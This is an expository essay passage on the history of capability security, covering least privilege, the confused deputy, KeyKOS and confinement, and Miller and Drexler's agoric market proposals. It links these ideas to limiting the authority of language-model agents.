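# Capability Security and AI Safety: From the Agoric Papers and Xanadu to Least-Privilege AI Agents

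## Capabilities, authority and least privilege explained

Capability security is an approach to computer security in which a program can act on a file, a device or another program only if it holds an unforgeable reference to it. This reference, called a capability, both names the object and carries the right to use it. Most everyday computers instead let a program do whatever the person who started it may do, so a card game has the same rights over that person's letters and tax files as the person does. A capability system starts the card game with no capabilities and grants them one at a time.

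Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn described capabilities in 1966. In the 1980s a circle of programmers took up the idea, centred on Eric Drexler, Mark S. Miller, the Xanadu hypertext project and the Foresight Institute. Drexler wrote about nanotechnology and its dangers, and helped found the institute, a non-profit. The circle held that large software systems should coordinate through markets and get their security from capabilities. Interest has returned in the 2020s because companies now let language models read mail, run commands and spend money, often through a person's own accounts, and nobody can list in advance everything such a model will do. If you can't vouch for how a program behaves, the obvious thing to try is limiting what it can reach. It is much less clear whether this works against a system that an attacker has misled or that has bad aims of its own.

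In writing about AI, "capability" usually means something a system is able to do, so a laboratory that runs "dangerous capability evaluations" is measuring skill. In capability security, the word refers to authority that a program holds, regardless of its skill. A twenty-line script may hold the capability to delete a company's customer records even if a highly skilled model holds none. "Ability" or "skill" is therefore a clearer word for what an AI system can do.

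### Least privilege, and two ways to copy a file

The standard statement of least privilege comes from *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975), which lists eight design principles. One is that every program and user should run with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". This limits the damage from an accident and leaves fewer programs to audit when someone suspects misuse of a privilege. Saltzer and Schroeder compare it to the military rule of "need-to-know".

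The principle itself was a little older. *The "Principle of Least Privilege" and Multics* (Saltzer, 1973), a working note on the Multics time-sharing system, credits it to David J. Edwards of the US National Security Agency. Saltzer's version is also stricter than the slogan. It says designers should make even *potential* unnecessary connections impossible, because somebody has to check each of them. In the innermost layer of Multics, any program that used pointer variables could reach any data in that layer, so anyone certifying one component there had to read all the other programs that used pointers to rule out interference.

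Ordinary operating systems make the principle very hard to follow. Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, show why with two Unix commands that both copy a file. Here is the usual one:

`cp foo.txt bar.txt`

The shell, the program that reads what the user types, passes `cp` two pieces of text, "foo.txt" and "bar.txt". To find the files, `cp` has to look those names up among all the user's files. The user could have typed any name, so `cp` must be able to open any file that the user can open. The least authority with which `cp` can do its job is therefore the user's whole authority over the file system, and asking its programmers to be more modest won't help. Now compare:

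`cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`

This time the shell opens both files and gives `cat` two file descriptors, small numbers that stand for open files, so `cat` doesn't need the file names. On a normal Unix machine `cat` still runs with all of the user's permissions, but the copy would succeed even if it had access only to the two open files.

The `cp` command relies on access control lists, which are attached to resources and record what each user may do to them. When `cp` asks to open foo.txt, the operating system checks the file's list for the user whose account `cp` is running under, and `cp` presents no specific grant of its own. Miller, Yee and Shapiro call this ambient authority in *Capability Myths Demolished*, meaning authority that a program exercises without selecting it. They compare it to a world with doors but no keys, where a door opens if the right person walks up. An open file descriptor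 is close to a capability, since whoever holds it can use the file without a further check.

Both methods are much older than computers, as the textbook chapter *Access Control* points out. A single table can represent both. If it lists users down the side, files across the top and permitted actions in the cells, each column is an access control list and each row is a user's list of capabilities. Miller and his co-authors call the belief that the two methods are therefore equivalent the Equivalence Myth. They argue that the table is a snapshot, which leaves out how a program refers to a file and who may change the cells.

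An access list points from the file to the user, so the program needs a separate name for the file, and it gets that name and the right to use the file by different routes. The list also needs stable names for its entries. People have stable names, but program runs start and stop all day, so administrators list people, and each run of a program inherits all of a person's rights. This second point applies to access lists as people build them in practice, since Miller and colleagues concede that nothing in the table itself forbids a finer-grained list.

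Peter Gutmann (2015) criticized the paper in a mailing-list thread that borrows its title, objecting that one can demolish any "myth" with well-picked examples and theoretical solutions that need not work in practice. In the same thread, Jerry Leichter complained that the paper "cheats a bit" by meeting each objection with an extension to the capability model. Bill Frantz (2015), whose comments are acknowledged in the paper, replied to Leichter and granted that the paper has "an overtone of annoyance". These complaints don't refute the `cp` example, but they bear on whether anyone can run a large, convenient system on capabilities. The critics had a point there. Lecture slides from Purdue University include the reasonable question of how one user would then share a file with another.

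### Permission and authority

The "privilege" in "least privilege" can mean either permission or authority. A permission is a direct right to act on an object. A program's authority is every effect it can cause, whether directly or through others that act on its requests.

Suppose Alice and Bob are programs. Bob has permission to write to a certain file. Alice does not, but she has permission to send messages to Bob. If Bob copies into the file whatever text Alice sends him, then Alice has authority to write to the file without having permission to do so. Neither program has broken a rule, but an auditor who reads only the list of permissions will wrongly report that the file is safe from Alice. Alice's authority depends on both the arrangement of permissions and how Bob behaves.

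This makes authority awkward to calculate. Miller, in his 2006 thesis *Robust Composition*, sets out the options as a chain of sets, each of which contains the one before it:

$$CP \subseteq EA \subseteq BA \subseteq TA$$

CP is the set of current permissions. It is easy to look up but unsafe to rely on, because it omits Alice's indirect route to the file. EA is eventual authority, the effects that programs really will be able to cause. It is the set one wants, but in general nobody can compute it, because it depends on what every program along the way will do. TA is the bound obtained from topology alone, by drawing an arrow for every permission, assuming that every program is hostile, and counting everything that anyone could reach along the arrows. It is easy to compute and safe, since if the pair "Alice, file" is absent from TA, it is also absent from EA. But relying on TA means rejecting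 many harmless arrangements. BA is a tighter bound that is still safe. It takes into account the known behaviour of a few programs, for example that Bob checks each line and refuses to overwrite old ones.

How much tighter BA is than TA depends on how well somebody understands Bob. A thirty-line filter is easy to understand, but if Bob is a language model, an engineer can guarantee very little about his behaviour, and BA moves closer to TA. Miller's definitions were informal, and *Permission and Authority Revisited* (Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues, 2016) later proposed formal versions for a small object-oriented language.

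Miller and Shapiro find it unclear whether Saltzer and Schroeder meant least permission or least authority. Authority is what matters for security, so capability programmers speak of the principle of least authority.

### How a program comes to hold a reference

Reasoning along the arrows only works if new arrows can't appear from nowhere. The object-capability model supplies that guarantee. It treats a running system as a collection of objects, pieces of code with their own stored data, that can affect each other only by sending messages along references they hold. Miller allows four ways in which an object Bob can come to hold a reference to an object Carol:

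- **Initial conditions.** Bob already held the reference when the system started, or when the analysis begins.
- **Parenthood.** Bob creates Carol. At that moment he is the only object that refers to her.
- **Endowment.** Alice, who already holds a reference to Carol, creates Bob and builds the reference into him.
- **Introduction.** Alice holds references to both Bob and Carol, and chooses to send Bob a message that contains the reference to Carol.

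Miller summarizes the rule as "only connectivity begets connectivity". If two groups of objects have no reference between them and no third party that can reach both, nothing either group does can connect them. If a single object bridges the two groups, any further connection between them depends on that object, so a reviewer knows which code to read. The same rule applies to file sharing. Alice shares a file by sending Bob a reference to it, which she can do only if she can already reach Bob.

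The argument fails if a program can get access to an object in a fifth way, and ordinary languages allow several. In C++, a program can turn an integer into a pointer, so it can reach an object by guessing its address. In Java, two objects that were never given references to each other can still exchange them through a shared global variable. The model has to forbid both. It makes an exception only for plain data, because a program can produce the number 7, or a secret key it manages to guess, without being given it.

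In 1984, W. E. Boebert used a gap of this kind to argue that capability machines cannot keep secrets. Suppose a system has a secret level and a public level, and the secret program may read public memory but must never write to it. The public program has a capability to write to public memory, and stores a copy of that capability there as if it were ordinary data. The secret program reads the copy and can then use it to write secrets into public memory. The attack works on any system in which a capability is just a string of bits, as Miller and colleagues accept. But they point out that nearly all capability systems keep capabilities and data apart, so the right to read data from a piece of memory does not include the right to fetch capabilities from it.

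A plain reference gives full and permanent use of its object, which is often more than Alice wants to give Bob. She can attenuate (weaken) that access by making an intermediate object that forwards only some requests, such as reads, and giving Bob a reference to that instead. If she keeps a way to switch off the intermediate object, she can later revoke Bob's access, and the reference he still holds will stop working.

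### The confused deputy

The best-known argument for capabilities is *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Norm Hardy's account of an accident at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Hardy calls it a "nearly true story" from about eleven years earlier.

Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates source code into machine instructions, in a directory called SYSX. A user who ran it could name a file to receive debugging output. The staff had also altered the compiler to record statistics on which language features people used in a file called STAT, also in SYSX. Users had no right to write there, so the staff gave the compiler a "home files license", which let it write to any file in its own directory. The company's billing records were in the same directory, in a file called BILL.

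Some user learned that name and entered it as the place for the debugging output. The compiler asked the operating system to open the file, and the operating system allowed this because the compiler had its licence. The compiler wrote the debugging output over the billing records.

It's hard to say what anyone should have fixed. The compiler could refuse output files in other directories, but users had good reasons to want them. It could refuse SYSX in particular, but that name did not exist when the programmers wrote the code, and some users might have a legitimate right to write there. It could refuse BILL, but then somebody would have to update the compiler whenever another sensitive file appeared. Limiting the compiler's licence to STAT would protect BILL, but a user could still name STAT as the output file and wipe out the statistics. Tymshare added a system call that let the compiler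 "switch hats" to declare whose authority it was using, but some applications soon needed more than two authorities. When Hardy last wrote down the conditions for a program to open a file, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

Hardy's diagnosis is that the compiler was a deputy with authority from two sources, the user and its licence, and could not indicate which one it was using for a given write. When the user named a file they had no right to write to, the operating system allowed the write because the compiler's licence permitted it.

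A capability always combines a reference to a file with permission to use it. The compiler uses a capability to STAT, supplied by the staff, to write statistics, and a capability to an output file, supplied by the user, to write debugging information. A user who isn't allowed to write to BILL has no capability to it to pass along, and typing the file's name doesn't provide one, so the compiler needs no list of forbidden names. The episode persuaded Hardy that capabilities were necessary, and he went on to work on KeyKOS, an operating system built on them.

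Miller and colleagues explain that capabilities prevent a deputy from being confused only if it keeps each one tied to the purpose for which it received it. They don't protect a deputy that tries every capability it holds until one works. A compiler's programmer can specify in the code which reference to use for statistics and which for debugging. But a language model chooses among its references as it runs, based on whatever text it has just read, and in a prompt injection attack, the attacker writes some of that text.

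## Capability machines and operating systems, 1966 to 1988

In the 1960s computers were so expensive that many people had to share one. Dennis and Van Horn, at MIT, were designing for machines that ran several people's programs at once. The programs shared memory and processor time, and they often had to use the same copy of data because a separate copy for every user would waste storage. The system therefore had to stop programs from interfering with each other while still letting them share data.

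Dennis and Van Horn gave each running computation a list of capabilities, or C-list. Each entry points to one object, such as a segment (a block of memory), and records whether the computation may run, read or write it. The program refers to an entry by its position in the list. To read word 40 of the segment at position 3, it gives the pair (3, 40). The supervisor, the trusted core of the system, then finds entry 3 and checks that it allows reading. The program can't refer to an object that isn't on the list, because that object has no position number.

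In the chapter *Early Capability Architectures* of *Capability Based Computer Systems*, Levy (1984) counts the "protected procedure" among the most important parts of the design. If Alice calls Bob's procedure, it runs with Bob's C-list instead of hers, plus one capability she passes in. She can't read Bob's private data, and his code can access hers only as that capability allows.

### What the early machines added, and what they cost

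MIT students used the first working version, on a small PDP-1 computer with five typewriter terminals, until the mid-1970s. It had capabilities only for large things such as tapes and terminals. In 1967, a group at the University of Chicago tried to build a more ambitious machine but never finished it. It would have had separate registers for capabilities and data, so that no program could compute a capability as if it were a number.

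Cambridge University finished a capability machine, the CAP computer. *The Cambridge CAP Computer and its protection system* (Needham and Walker, 1977) describes how it applied least privilege to every module within a program. This required a special processor, with the protection partly in its circuits and partly in microprogram, the low-level code that carries out a processor's instructions.

Hydra, built at Carnegie Mellon University in the 1970s, let programmers define new kinds of object, each with its own rights. Someone who defined a mailbox could let one program add messages and another remove them, and the kernel (the part of an operating system with full control of the machine) would protect mailboxes as it protected files. But Hydra did this in software on ordinary minicomputer processors, and a call between protected procedures took far longer than a normal call. Such slow calls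 discourage programmers from dividing their work into the small, separately protected pieces that least privilege requires.

IBM's System/38, a business computer of the late 1970s, had capabilities, which IBM called "pointers". Each took up 16 bytes. Hidden tag bits, which required special memory, marked the genuine pointers, so the machine rejected any that a program had overwritten with ordinary data. IBM also kept conventional records of what each user could do, so the System/38 was only partly a capability machine. It sold well, and its descendants are still on the market as IBM i.

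Complexity could harm a capability system as much as slowness. Butler Lampson's *Reflections on an Operating System Design* reviews a capability system for Berkeley's CDC 6400 computer. Its designers built it in layers, each protected from faults in the layers above, but had serious trouble keeping the layers separate once they added more levels of storage.

### The confinement problem

Lampson's *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973) describes a problem that least privilege alone doesn't solve. Suppose a customer gives her financial records to someone else's program to calculate her tax. The program has to read the records, so she needs some other way to be sure that it won't pass them to its owner.

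The program could leak the records by writing them into a file that its owner can read, or by remembering them and reporting them later. Billing is more awkward because the owner has to learn something about each use in order to charge for it. *Protection*, an earlier paper by Lampson, gives the example of a compiler whose owner charges by the number of statements compiled. A dishonest program could hide information in that number.

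The hardest leaks to stop use covert channels, which are paths that nobody meant for communication. *Security in KeyKOS*, by Rajunas, Hardy and colleagues, mentions one that depends on how long a computer takes to read a page, a fixed-size block of storage. Suppose the tax program and an accomplice can both read a set of pages but can't write to them. To send a 1, the tax program reads a page, which brings it from disk into memory. To send a 0, it leaves the page alone. The accomplice then times its own read of that page, taking a fast read as 1 and a slow read as 0. At one bit a second, a 128-bit encryption key would leak in about two minutes, and each program would have read only what it was allowed to read.

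### Keys and domains in KeyKOS

Tymshare, the company in Hardy's story of the overwritten billing file, had a commercial reason to care about confinement. Some of its customers could own valuable programs and others valuable data, and they had no particular reason to trust each other. *The KeyKOS Nanokernel Architecture*, by Bomberger, Frantz and colleagues, lists three requirements for the operating system that Tymshare began in 1975: more accurate accounting than anyone then offered, service around the clock, and strong security between "mutually suspicious" customers using the machine at the same time.

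The engineers called the system GNOSIS, for Great New Operating System In the Sky. It began running production work on an IBM mainframe in January 1983. Key Logic, a company formed in 1985 to take over its development, renamed it KeyKOS.

KeyKOS calls capabilities keys and stores them separately from data. A node holds sixteen keys, and a page holds 4,096 bytes of data. Each program runs in a domain, which is roughly the running program together with its memory and keys. The program cannot read the bits that make up a key, so when it calls the kernel to use one, it identifies the key by its slot, such as slot 5.

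Using a key sends a message to the object that the key designates. The message can carry data and up to four keys. If the sender wants an answer, the kernel adds a "resume key", and all copies of that key stop working after the first use. The receiving domain doesn't learn who called it and gains none of the caller's authority except the keys in the message.

The same rule covers things that most systems provide automatically. Hardy (1985), in *KeyKOS Architecture*, notes that a domain has no terminal or file directory unless it holds a key to one. To run, it needs a key to a meter, which limits its processor time, and it gets storage through a key to a "space bank".

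This message-passing could have made the system unusably slow, so the designers worked hard to make calls fast. Rajunas and colleagues reported in 1986 that a call took about 200 machine instructions, and Bomberger and colleagues later reported 90 for the message path on the same family of mainframes.

### Running a secret program on secret data

The KeyKOS answer to confinement was the factory, a trusted object that makes new domains of one particular kind. Here is how the owner of a secret program could let a customer run it on secret data:

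1. The program's owner puts it into a factory, along with any keys it needs, and seals the factory.
2. The customer receives a key to the factory and passes it to a factory of her own, which inspects the keys that the new domain would hold.
3. If none of them could carry information out, she orders a domain, built from storage in her own space bank.
4. She sends it her data and gets the results back.

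The inspection in step 2 rejects any key that could influence something outside. For example, if the owner had included a key to his own space bank, the program could allocate storage there and fill it with copies of her data. Her factory would find the key and refuse to certify the product. The factory can find every key because the system stores keys separately from data. Some keys are harmless, including "sense keys", which allow only reading. Any key that a program fetches through a sense key is also reduced to read-only access or made useless.

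The owner is protected too, because the customer's key lets her send messages to the new domain but not examine its code. Hardy (1986) adds in *Computer security system*, his patent on the factory, that sealing the factory leaves the builder with only one special type of key to it, so he can't change the program after the customer has checked it.

The check works without anyone reading the program, because the customer's safety depends on which keys the program holds. It therefore works just as well on code that is malicious or that nobody understands. The customer does have to trust the factory and the rest of the trusted computing base (the parts of the system that must work correctly). In 1986 that came to 25,000 lines of kernel code and another 25,000 outside the kernel.

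Rajunas and colleagues accept that covert timing channels were still possible in KeyKOS, though they say that other activity on the machine would obscure the signal. That is a weak defence, because a program can send every bit many times. Their better suggestion was to show programs an artificial clock. IBM had tried this experimentally but didn't offer it as a product.

### Keeping capabilities alive through a crash

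On most computers, running programs are lost when the power fails, along with any capabilities they held in memory. File names survive on disk, so after a restart the system has to decide again who may open what, and an access list is the natural way to do it. A system that relies entirely on capabilities has to preserve them across restarts.

KeyKOS saved the state of the whole machine every few minutes. It briefly paused all programs while it noted which pages had changed, then let them continue as it copied those pages to one of two reserved areas on disk. After finishing the copy, KeyKOS gradually moved the pages to their permanent places and used the other area for the next checkpoint. A crash during this process could not leave the saved state half-written, because the previous complete checkpoint was still on disk. Since nodes were part of the checkpoint, every program came back with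 the keys it had held when the checkpoint was taken, and the outage looked to the program like a sudden jump in the clock.

Bomberger and colleagues say that Key Logic unplugged its machine on request at a 1990 trade show, and that everything was back on the screen within 30 seconds of power returning. A crash could still erase a few minutes of work, which is too much to lose when handling a bank's transactions, so KeyKOS let programs save particular pages immediately.

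### Why Unix won

Unix spread even though it gives each program its user's full rights, and speed doesn't seem to be the reason. In 1990 Key Logic built KeyNIX, a version of Unix that ran on top of KeyKOS, and Bomberger and colleagues compared it with Mach 2.5, another Unix system, on the same model of computer:

| Operation | KeyNIX | Mach 2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Open and close a file | 714 per second | 2,777 per second |
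| Start and end a process | 64 per second | 10 per second |
| Send data through a pipe between two processes | 0.588 MB per second | 1.05 MB per second |
| Write and read a test file | 4 seconds | 26 seconds |

These are the developers' own figures, from what they call a limited comparison. One programmer had written KeyNIX in six months. Opening files was slow because the design put every file's record in a separate domain, a choice the developers regretted. Still, the results hardly show that capabilities were too slow to sell.

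Compatibility is a likelier explanation. Existing programs were written to open files by name with their user's rights. Customers could run them unchanged on KeyNIX, but each program then had its user's full authority inside that copy of Unix, and finer protection required rewriting it. By the time KeyKOS left the mainframe, Unix was already established on workstations and in universities. Access lists also let administrators look up directly who can read a file, while in a capability system they have to trace who holds which keys. And KeyKOS was hard to learn. Rajunas and colleagues report complaints about its vocabulary, and themselves call "domain creator creator" an unfortunate term.

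### The military secrecy objection

The armed forces might have been a natural market, but many specialists thought capabilities couldn't enforce military secrecy rules. Those rules forbid anyone with secret material from giving it to someone without clearance, even if both people want to share it. In a capability system, anyone who holds a capability can normally pass it on. This objection is broader than Boebert's attack, which depended on capabilities being stored as ordinary data.

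One common fix was to put a security label in every capability and check it at each use. Rajunas and colleagues rejected this because central checks would slow the system down, and because the kernel handles pages and nodes and can't identify the documents the rules cover. They let capabilities be copied freely and controlled the connections instead. An administrator divides the system into compartments at the start, with no capabilities connecting them. By Miller's connectivity rule, no such capabilities can ever appear.

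Completely isolated compartments aren't much use, so KeyKOS allowed some access between them. Programs in a secret compartment could hold sense keys to public files, which let them read everything in the files but write nothing. KeyKOS called any stronger key out of a compartment a "hole". A hole had to lead to a trusted program, which might label a document before releasing it.

This answers the objection for direct leaks, but the rules also required records of who could reach what, and in 1986 that part existed only as a prototype. KeyKOS could revoke access by destroying an intermediate object, but two programs that had been free to exchange keys might have set up other connections before then. Key Logic still aimed to meet the upper B levels of the US Defense Department's security criteria with a version called KeySAFE, according to the library of KeyKOS papers published by Agorics, a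 software company.

### Successors, and the link to Miller's circle

Key Logic went out of business in the early 1990s, and licensing KeyKOS became impractical. Jonathan Shapiro, a co-author of the nanokernel paper, had begun rebuilding the design from its public documents in 1991, as a system he called EROS. In 2000 he and Samuel Weber published a proof that its confinement mechanism works, though the proof covers a mathematical model and not the code. EROS remained a research system. Shapiro dropped it in the mid-2000s for a successor, Coyotos, whose development had stopped by 2009. The EROS code continued as an open-source project, CapROS.

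A tribute on the memorial site ForeverMissed (2018) calls Hardy "the source of all modern thinking about capabilities" and says that by the 1990s only ideas rooted in KeyKOS were still growing. That is generous, given IBM's sales, but it fits the circle around Mark Miller. Shapiro wrote *Paradigm Regained* with Miller, and Bill Frantz, a KeyKOS developer, defended *Capability Myths Demolished* against its critics. In the mailing-list thread *Questions about KeyKOS*, Miller (2019) recalls dreaming of using his programming language E to join several KeyKOS machines into one distributed capability system. He knew of no attempt to do this with KeyKOS or its descendants, among which he includes the seL4 kernel. Hardy had moved closer to the circle by 1992, when the nanokernel paper gave a xanadu.com address for enquiries to him.

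## The 1988 proposal for markets inside computers

Mark Miller met Eric Drexler in about 1979 at a conference on space industry in Princeton. Miller was working on Xanadu with its founder, Ted Nelson, and Drexler was presenting light sails, which use sunlight to push a spacecraft. In an interview published by Agoric, a company he later co-founded, Miller recalls explaining object-oriented programming to Drexler, particularly encapsulation, the rule that other code can reach an object's data only by sending the object a message. Drexler replied that it was like Friedrich Hayek's explanation of why property rights are useful. Miller says this remark did more than anything else to start their joint work.

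The economist Hayek asked how millions of people can carry out their plans without knowing each other's and without constantly getting in each other's way. Part of his answer was property. A farmer with sole control of a field can plan the harvest without knowing what the neighbours intend. Encapsulation similarly lets programmers rely on an object's data staying as they left it, whatever other programmers are doing. Miller and Drexler (1988) wrote in *Markets and Computation* that computer science "has reinvented the notion of property rights".

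That paper sets out the whole scheme and is one of three that the pair contributed to *The Ecology of Computation*, a book edited by Bernardo Huberman. In *Incentive Engineering for Computational Resource Management*, Drexler and Miller (1988) design the auctions and rents. *Comparative Ecology* (1988) compares markets with biological ecosystems and with EURISKO, an AI program that evolved its own rules of thumb. The paper favours a "direct market", in which a program that earns more gets more computing power and spreads in altered copies. The pair called their systems agoric, after the agora, the Greek meeting and market place.

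### Prices in place of central rules

Encapsulation had given programs something like property rights over their data, but operating systems still allocated processor time and memory by central rules. The usual rule for processor time, round-robin scheduling, gives every process a turn. *Markets and Computation* calls this a commons, because anyone can take a larger share by starting more processes. If four people run one process each, each person gets a quarter of the processor time. If one of them then starts six more, that person gets seven of every ten turns and the others get one each.

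Miller and Drexler wanted hardware owners to charge for the use of their machines. A program would pay for its processor time and memory, pass the cost on to the program that requested its services, and perhaps add a royalty for its author. The person at the end of the chain would pay the whole bill. If that person also owned the machine, the money would only circulate, but the prices would still reflect what other programs needed.

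Prices can carry more of this information than priorities. In the paper's example, the faster of two machines has special hardware for numerical work. A fluid-flow simulation needs that hardware badly, while a theorem prover has higher priority but would gain only a little from the faster machine. A priority rule would give the faster machine to the theorem prover. With prices, the simulation would bid almost nothing for time on the slower machine, so that time would be cheap and the theorem prover would do well to buy it.

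Trading has costs, such as advertising, negotiation and bookkeeping. In 1937 the economist Ronald Coase used such costs to explain why firms exist, and Miller and Drexler expected the same thing inside computers. Small objects would group into "firms" that planned centrally and traded only with outsiders. Some evidence also suggested that traders didn't need to be clever. In laboratory auctions where people could communicate only through bids and acceptances, prices soon settled near the level that economic theory calls optimal. Spencer Star got similar efficiency from software traders with simple decision rules.

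### Why the market needs capabilities

Under the paper's definition, an agoric system must have foundations for encapsulating and communicating information, access and resources. An object can keep any of these to itself (encapsulation) or choose to hand it over (communication). Information means an object's contents, access means the right to send messages to another object, and resources are things such as a block of memory or a slice of processor time.

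Without this protection, trade would break down. If others could read a program's contents, they could steal whatever made it worth paying for. If they could alter its contents, customers couldn't rely on how it would behave. If programs could use resources without paying, parasites would spread. And if any object could send messages to any other, even the smallest would have to check that each message was legitimate, which Miller and Drexler thought would be too much overhead for small objects. With capabilities, the creator of an object controls who gets a reference to it, so the object can serve every caller without checking.

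Three of Miller's four ways of obtaining a reference, all except initial conditions, already appear in this paper.

Miller and Drexler argue that an insecure system can't be made secure by running an interpreter for a secure language on top of it. Any general-purpose language can run such an interpreter, since all of them can compute the same functions. But "security rests on inabilities", and adding an interpreter can't take abilities away from the system underneath. For example, the base system might let any program write to any memory address. The secure language has no instruction for this, so objects inside the interpreter are safe from each other, but a program running outside the interpreter can still overwrite the memory that holds those objects, including their account balances.

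This argument doesn't rule out interpreters altogether. If every untrusted program has to run inside the interpreter, none can attack it from outside. The paper accepts a secure interpreter as one way to separate objects within a sealed machine.

Miller later came to consider these foundations more urgent than prices. In the Agoric interview, he says the important early step is a system of rights that lets people combine programs written separately, "mostly in ignorance of each other".

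### An auction for sleeping bidders

A process can bid for the processor only while it is running, which requires already having the processor. Drexler and Miller compare this to "trying to auction wakeup pills to a sleeping crowd". They solve it by making bids rise automatically. Before a process goes to sleep, it leaves a bid on one of several "escalators", each of which raises bids at its own fixed rate. In each time slice, the processor runs the process with the highest bid and charges it the second-highest bid.

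Charging the winner the second-highest bid removes the incentive to guess what others will offer. A bidder does best by bidding what the slice is worth to it, because bidding more risks overpaying and bidding less risks losing a slice worth buying.

In this invented example, an editor's and a report generator's bids both start at zero, rising by 5 per slice for the editor and 2 for the report generator. An archiving job always bids 7. The table begins after one slice of waiting. A process that has just run enters a new bid on the same terms.

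| Slice | Editor | Report generator | Archiving job | Winner | Price paid |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5 | 2 | 7 | Archiving job | 5 |
| 2 | 10 | 4 | 7 | Editor | 7 |
| 3 | 0 | 6 | 7 | Archiving job | 6 |
| 4 | 5 | 8 | 7 | Report generator | 7 |
| 5 | 10 | 0 | 7 | Editor | 7 |

The report generator wins slice 4 without waking up to raise its bid. If the price stayed above 7, the archiving job would never run, which is the right result for work worth no more than 7.

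When the price is steady, a process whose bid always restarts from zero gets a share of the processor roughly equal to the bid's rate of increase divided by the price. If slices cost 100 and the bid rises by 2 per slice, it takes about 50 slices to reach the price, so the process gets about one slice in 50.

The auction house can also cap opening bids, so that new bids can't keep overtaking those already waiting. A bid on the fastest escalator eventually passes the cap, and no later bid can then overtake it, so its process will run if its owner can pay. If all processes start from zero on that escalator, the result is ordinary round-robin scheduling, which programmers who don't care about prices can use as their default.

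### Rent for storage

A system also needs a way to determine when to free memory. Most modern languages use garbage collection, which finds objects that no running program can reach and reuses their space. Drexler and Miller proposed that objects pay rent to programs called landlords, which own the storage and set the rent by auction. An object pays from what it earns when others use it. If it is needed but seldom used, it charges a retainer fee to each of its clients, the objects that hold references to it. An object that can't pay its rent loses its space.

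Rent can remove a kind of garbage that is hard to detect when it spans several companies' machines. Suppose three companies each have one object on their own machine. The objects refer to each other in a circle, and nothing else refers to them. Each object has a reference from another machine, so no company can tell from its own records that its object is useless. The companies could find out by moving all three objects to one machine, but then that machine's owner could read the others' data.

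If each of the three objects starts with 20 units of money and pays 5 units of rent per period, 15 units leave the circle each period. The objects can collect retainers from each other, but this only moves money around the circle. After four periods all 60 units are gone, and each landlord evicts its object without anyone having to look inside it.

Dividing the retainer among several clients is harder, because clients can cheat if the shares are equal. Suppose three clients split a rent of 30, at 10 each. If two of them reach the object through a shared go-between, the object has only two direct clients, the go-between and the third client, and charges each 15. The two clients who share the go-between then pay only 7.50 each.

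Drexler and Miller's solution is to treat the retainer as an investment. Each client $i$ reports the number of times it expects to use the object, $N_i$, and pays a matching share of the total fee $F$:

$$S_i = F\,\frac{N_i}{\sum_k N_k}$$

Each later use then costs a surcharge of $F/\sum_k N_k$, which the object pays out to its clients in proportion to what they invested.

Suppose the fee is 12, a program called Alice will use the object three times, and another called Bob will use it once. If both report this correctly, Alice pays 9 and Bob pays 3. Each use costs 3, and the payouts cancel the surcharges, so their final costs are also 9 and 3.

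If Bob reports 0 to avoid the retainer, the surcharge rises to 12/3, so his single use costs him 4. If he reports 3, he pays 6 at the start and 2 for his use, then gets 4 back, for a total of 4. Reporting the truth costs him only 3, as long as Alice's report is also correct. Drexler and Miller concede that a client who knows enough about the others' errors can gain by misreporting.

The rest of the storage scheme is shakier. An object that is about to lose its space alerts its clients, which pass the alert on to theirs until one of them can pay. If the chain is long, the money may arrive too late, and the landlord will delete something that a program still needs. Moving such objects to slower storage instead of deleting them would make these delays less harmful. The paper also says its code for the alerts "has not been run", and it recommends the scheme only for objects large enough to justify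 the overhead.

### Agents, bonds and reputations

A small program that sorts lists has no room for code that negotiates prices or detects fraud. *Markets and Computation* proposes handing this work to business agents, larger programs whose cost many small ones share. For example, programmers can build a lookup table in several ways, some faster and some using less memory. An agent could choose a version based on current prices, monitor how the customer uses the table, and switch if another version would be cheaper.

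The customer still has to decide which agents and suppliers to trust. If new names are easy to create, a cheat can escape a blacklist by returning under another name. Miller and Drexler therefore expected markets to rely on positive reputation, where customers look for names with a good record. A cheat who starts again under a new name then has no record to attract customers. This works as long as nobody can use someone else's name, which unforgeable references or digital signatures can ensure.

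Newcomers have no track record, but they can post a bond. If a new supplier could gain 20 by doing bad work but would forfeit a bond of 100, it has no financial reason to cheat. Both sides have to trust someone to hold the money and someone to judge the work, so bonds are most useful where quality is easy to check.

A seller with many names could also buy its own services and praise them. The paper proposes rating services that buy anonymously, as restaurant critics do, and sell what they learn. Customers would need to trust the rating services too, so those services would also face anonymous tests.

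### Why nobody had built one

Ivan Sutherland had already described a system in which people bid tokens on paper for blocks of computer time. But in 1988 nobody had built the kind of market that Miller and Drexler wanted, and they gave three reasons. There was no pressing need, because better programming tools had let one person, or a small team whose members trusted each other, manage ever larger programs. In small systems, the work of bookkeeping outweighs its benefits. And the large research networks served universities and government, where people who wrote useful software already gained a reputation for it. Miller and Drexler had found no obstacle to building agoric systems and expected them to become worthwhile as networks grew.

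Networks grew enormously, but ordinary schedulers still share out most processor time without an auction, so size alone was evidently not enough to bring in markets. Miller's later account in the Agoric interview is more convincing, and its claim is much narrower than the one from 1988. He says that programs in a Google data centre can declare their own priorities because the company controls who gets in and has other ways to deal with abuse. Strangers who share a machine have no such control over each other. His example is Ethereum, a blockchain that charges a fee called gas for the computation a program uses. Miller says that prices are needed there to avoid terrible allocations of resources, even if they don't produce the best ones.

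Several groups built computational markets in the 1990s. In 1992 Carl Waldspurger and colleagues described Spawn, a system from Xerox's research centre in Palo Alto in which programs bid in second-price auctions for idle time on networked workstations. In 1993 Michael Wellman published a method he called market-oriented programming. The programmer describes a problem as an economy of consumers and producers, software adjusts the prices until supply meets demand, and the amounts traded at those prices are the solution. Wellman tried this on transport networks, where one designer had written all the traders, so fraud wasn't an issue. Mariposa, a distributed database from the University of California, Berkeley, gave each query a budget and let the computers on its network bid to do the work.

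The subject reached economists too, and *The Journal of Economic Perspectives* published *Distributed Computation as an Economic System* in 1995. But none of these systems replaced ordinary schedulers or databases.

### Language models as buyers and sellers

In 1988 Miller and Drexler had to argue that very simple programs could trade. Language models can now read an offer, ask questions about it and bargain, and companies have begun to build shopping and customer-service agents on them. In *Virtual Agent Economies*, a Google DeepMind paper, Tomašev, Franklin and colleagues (2025) expect a vast economy of such agents to arise without anyone designing it.

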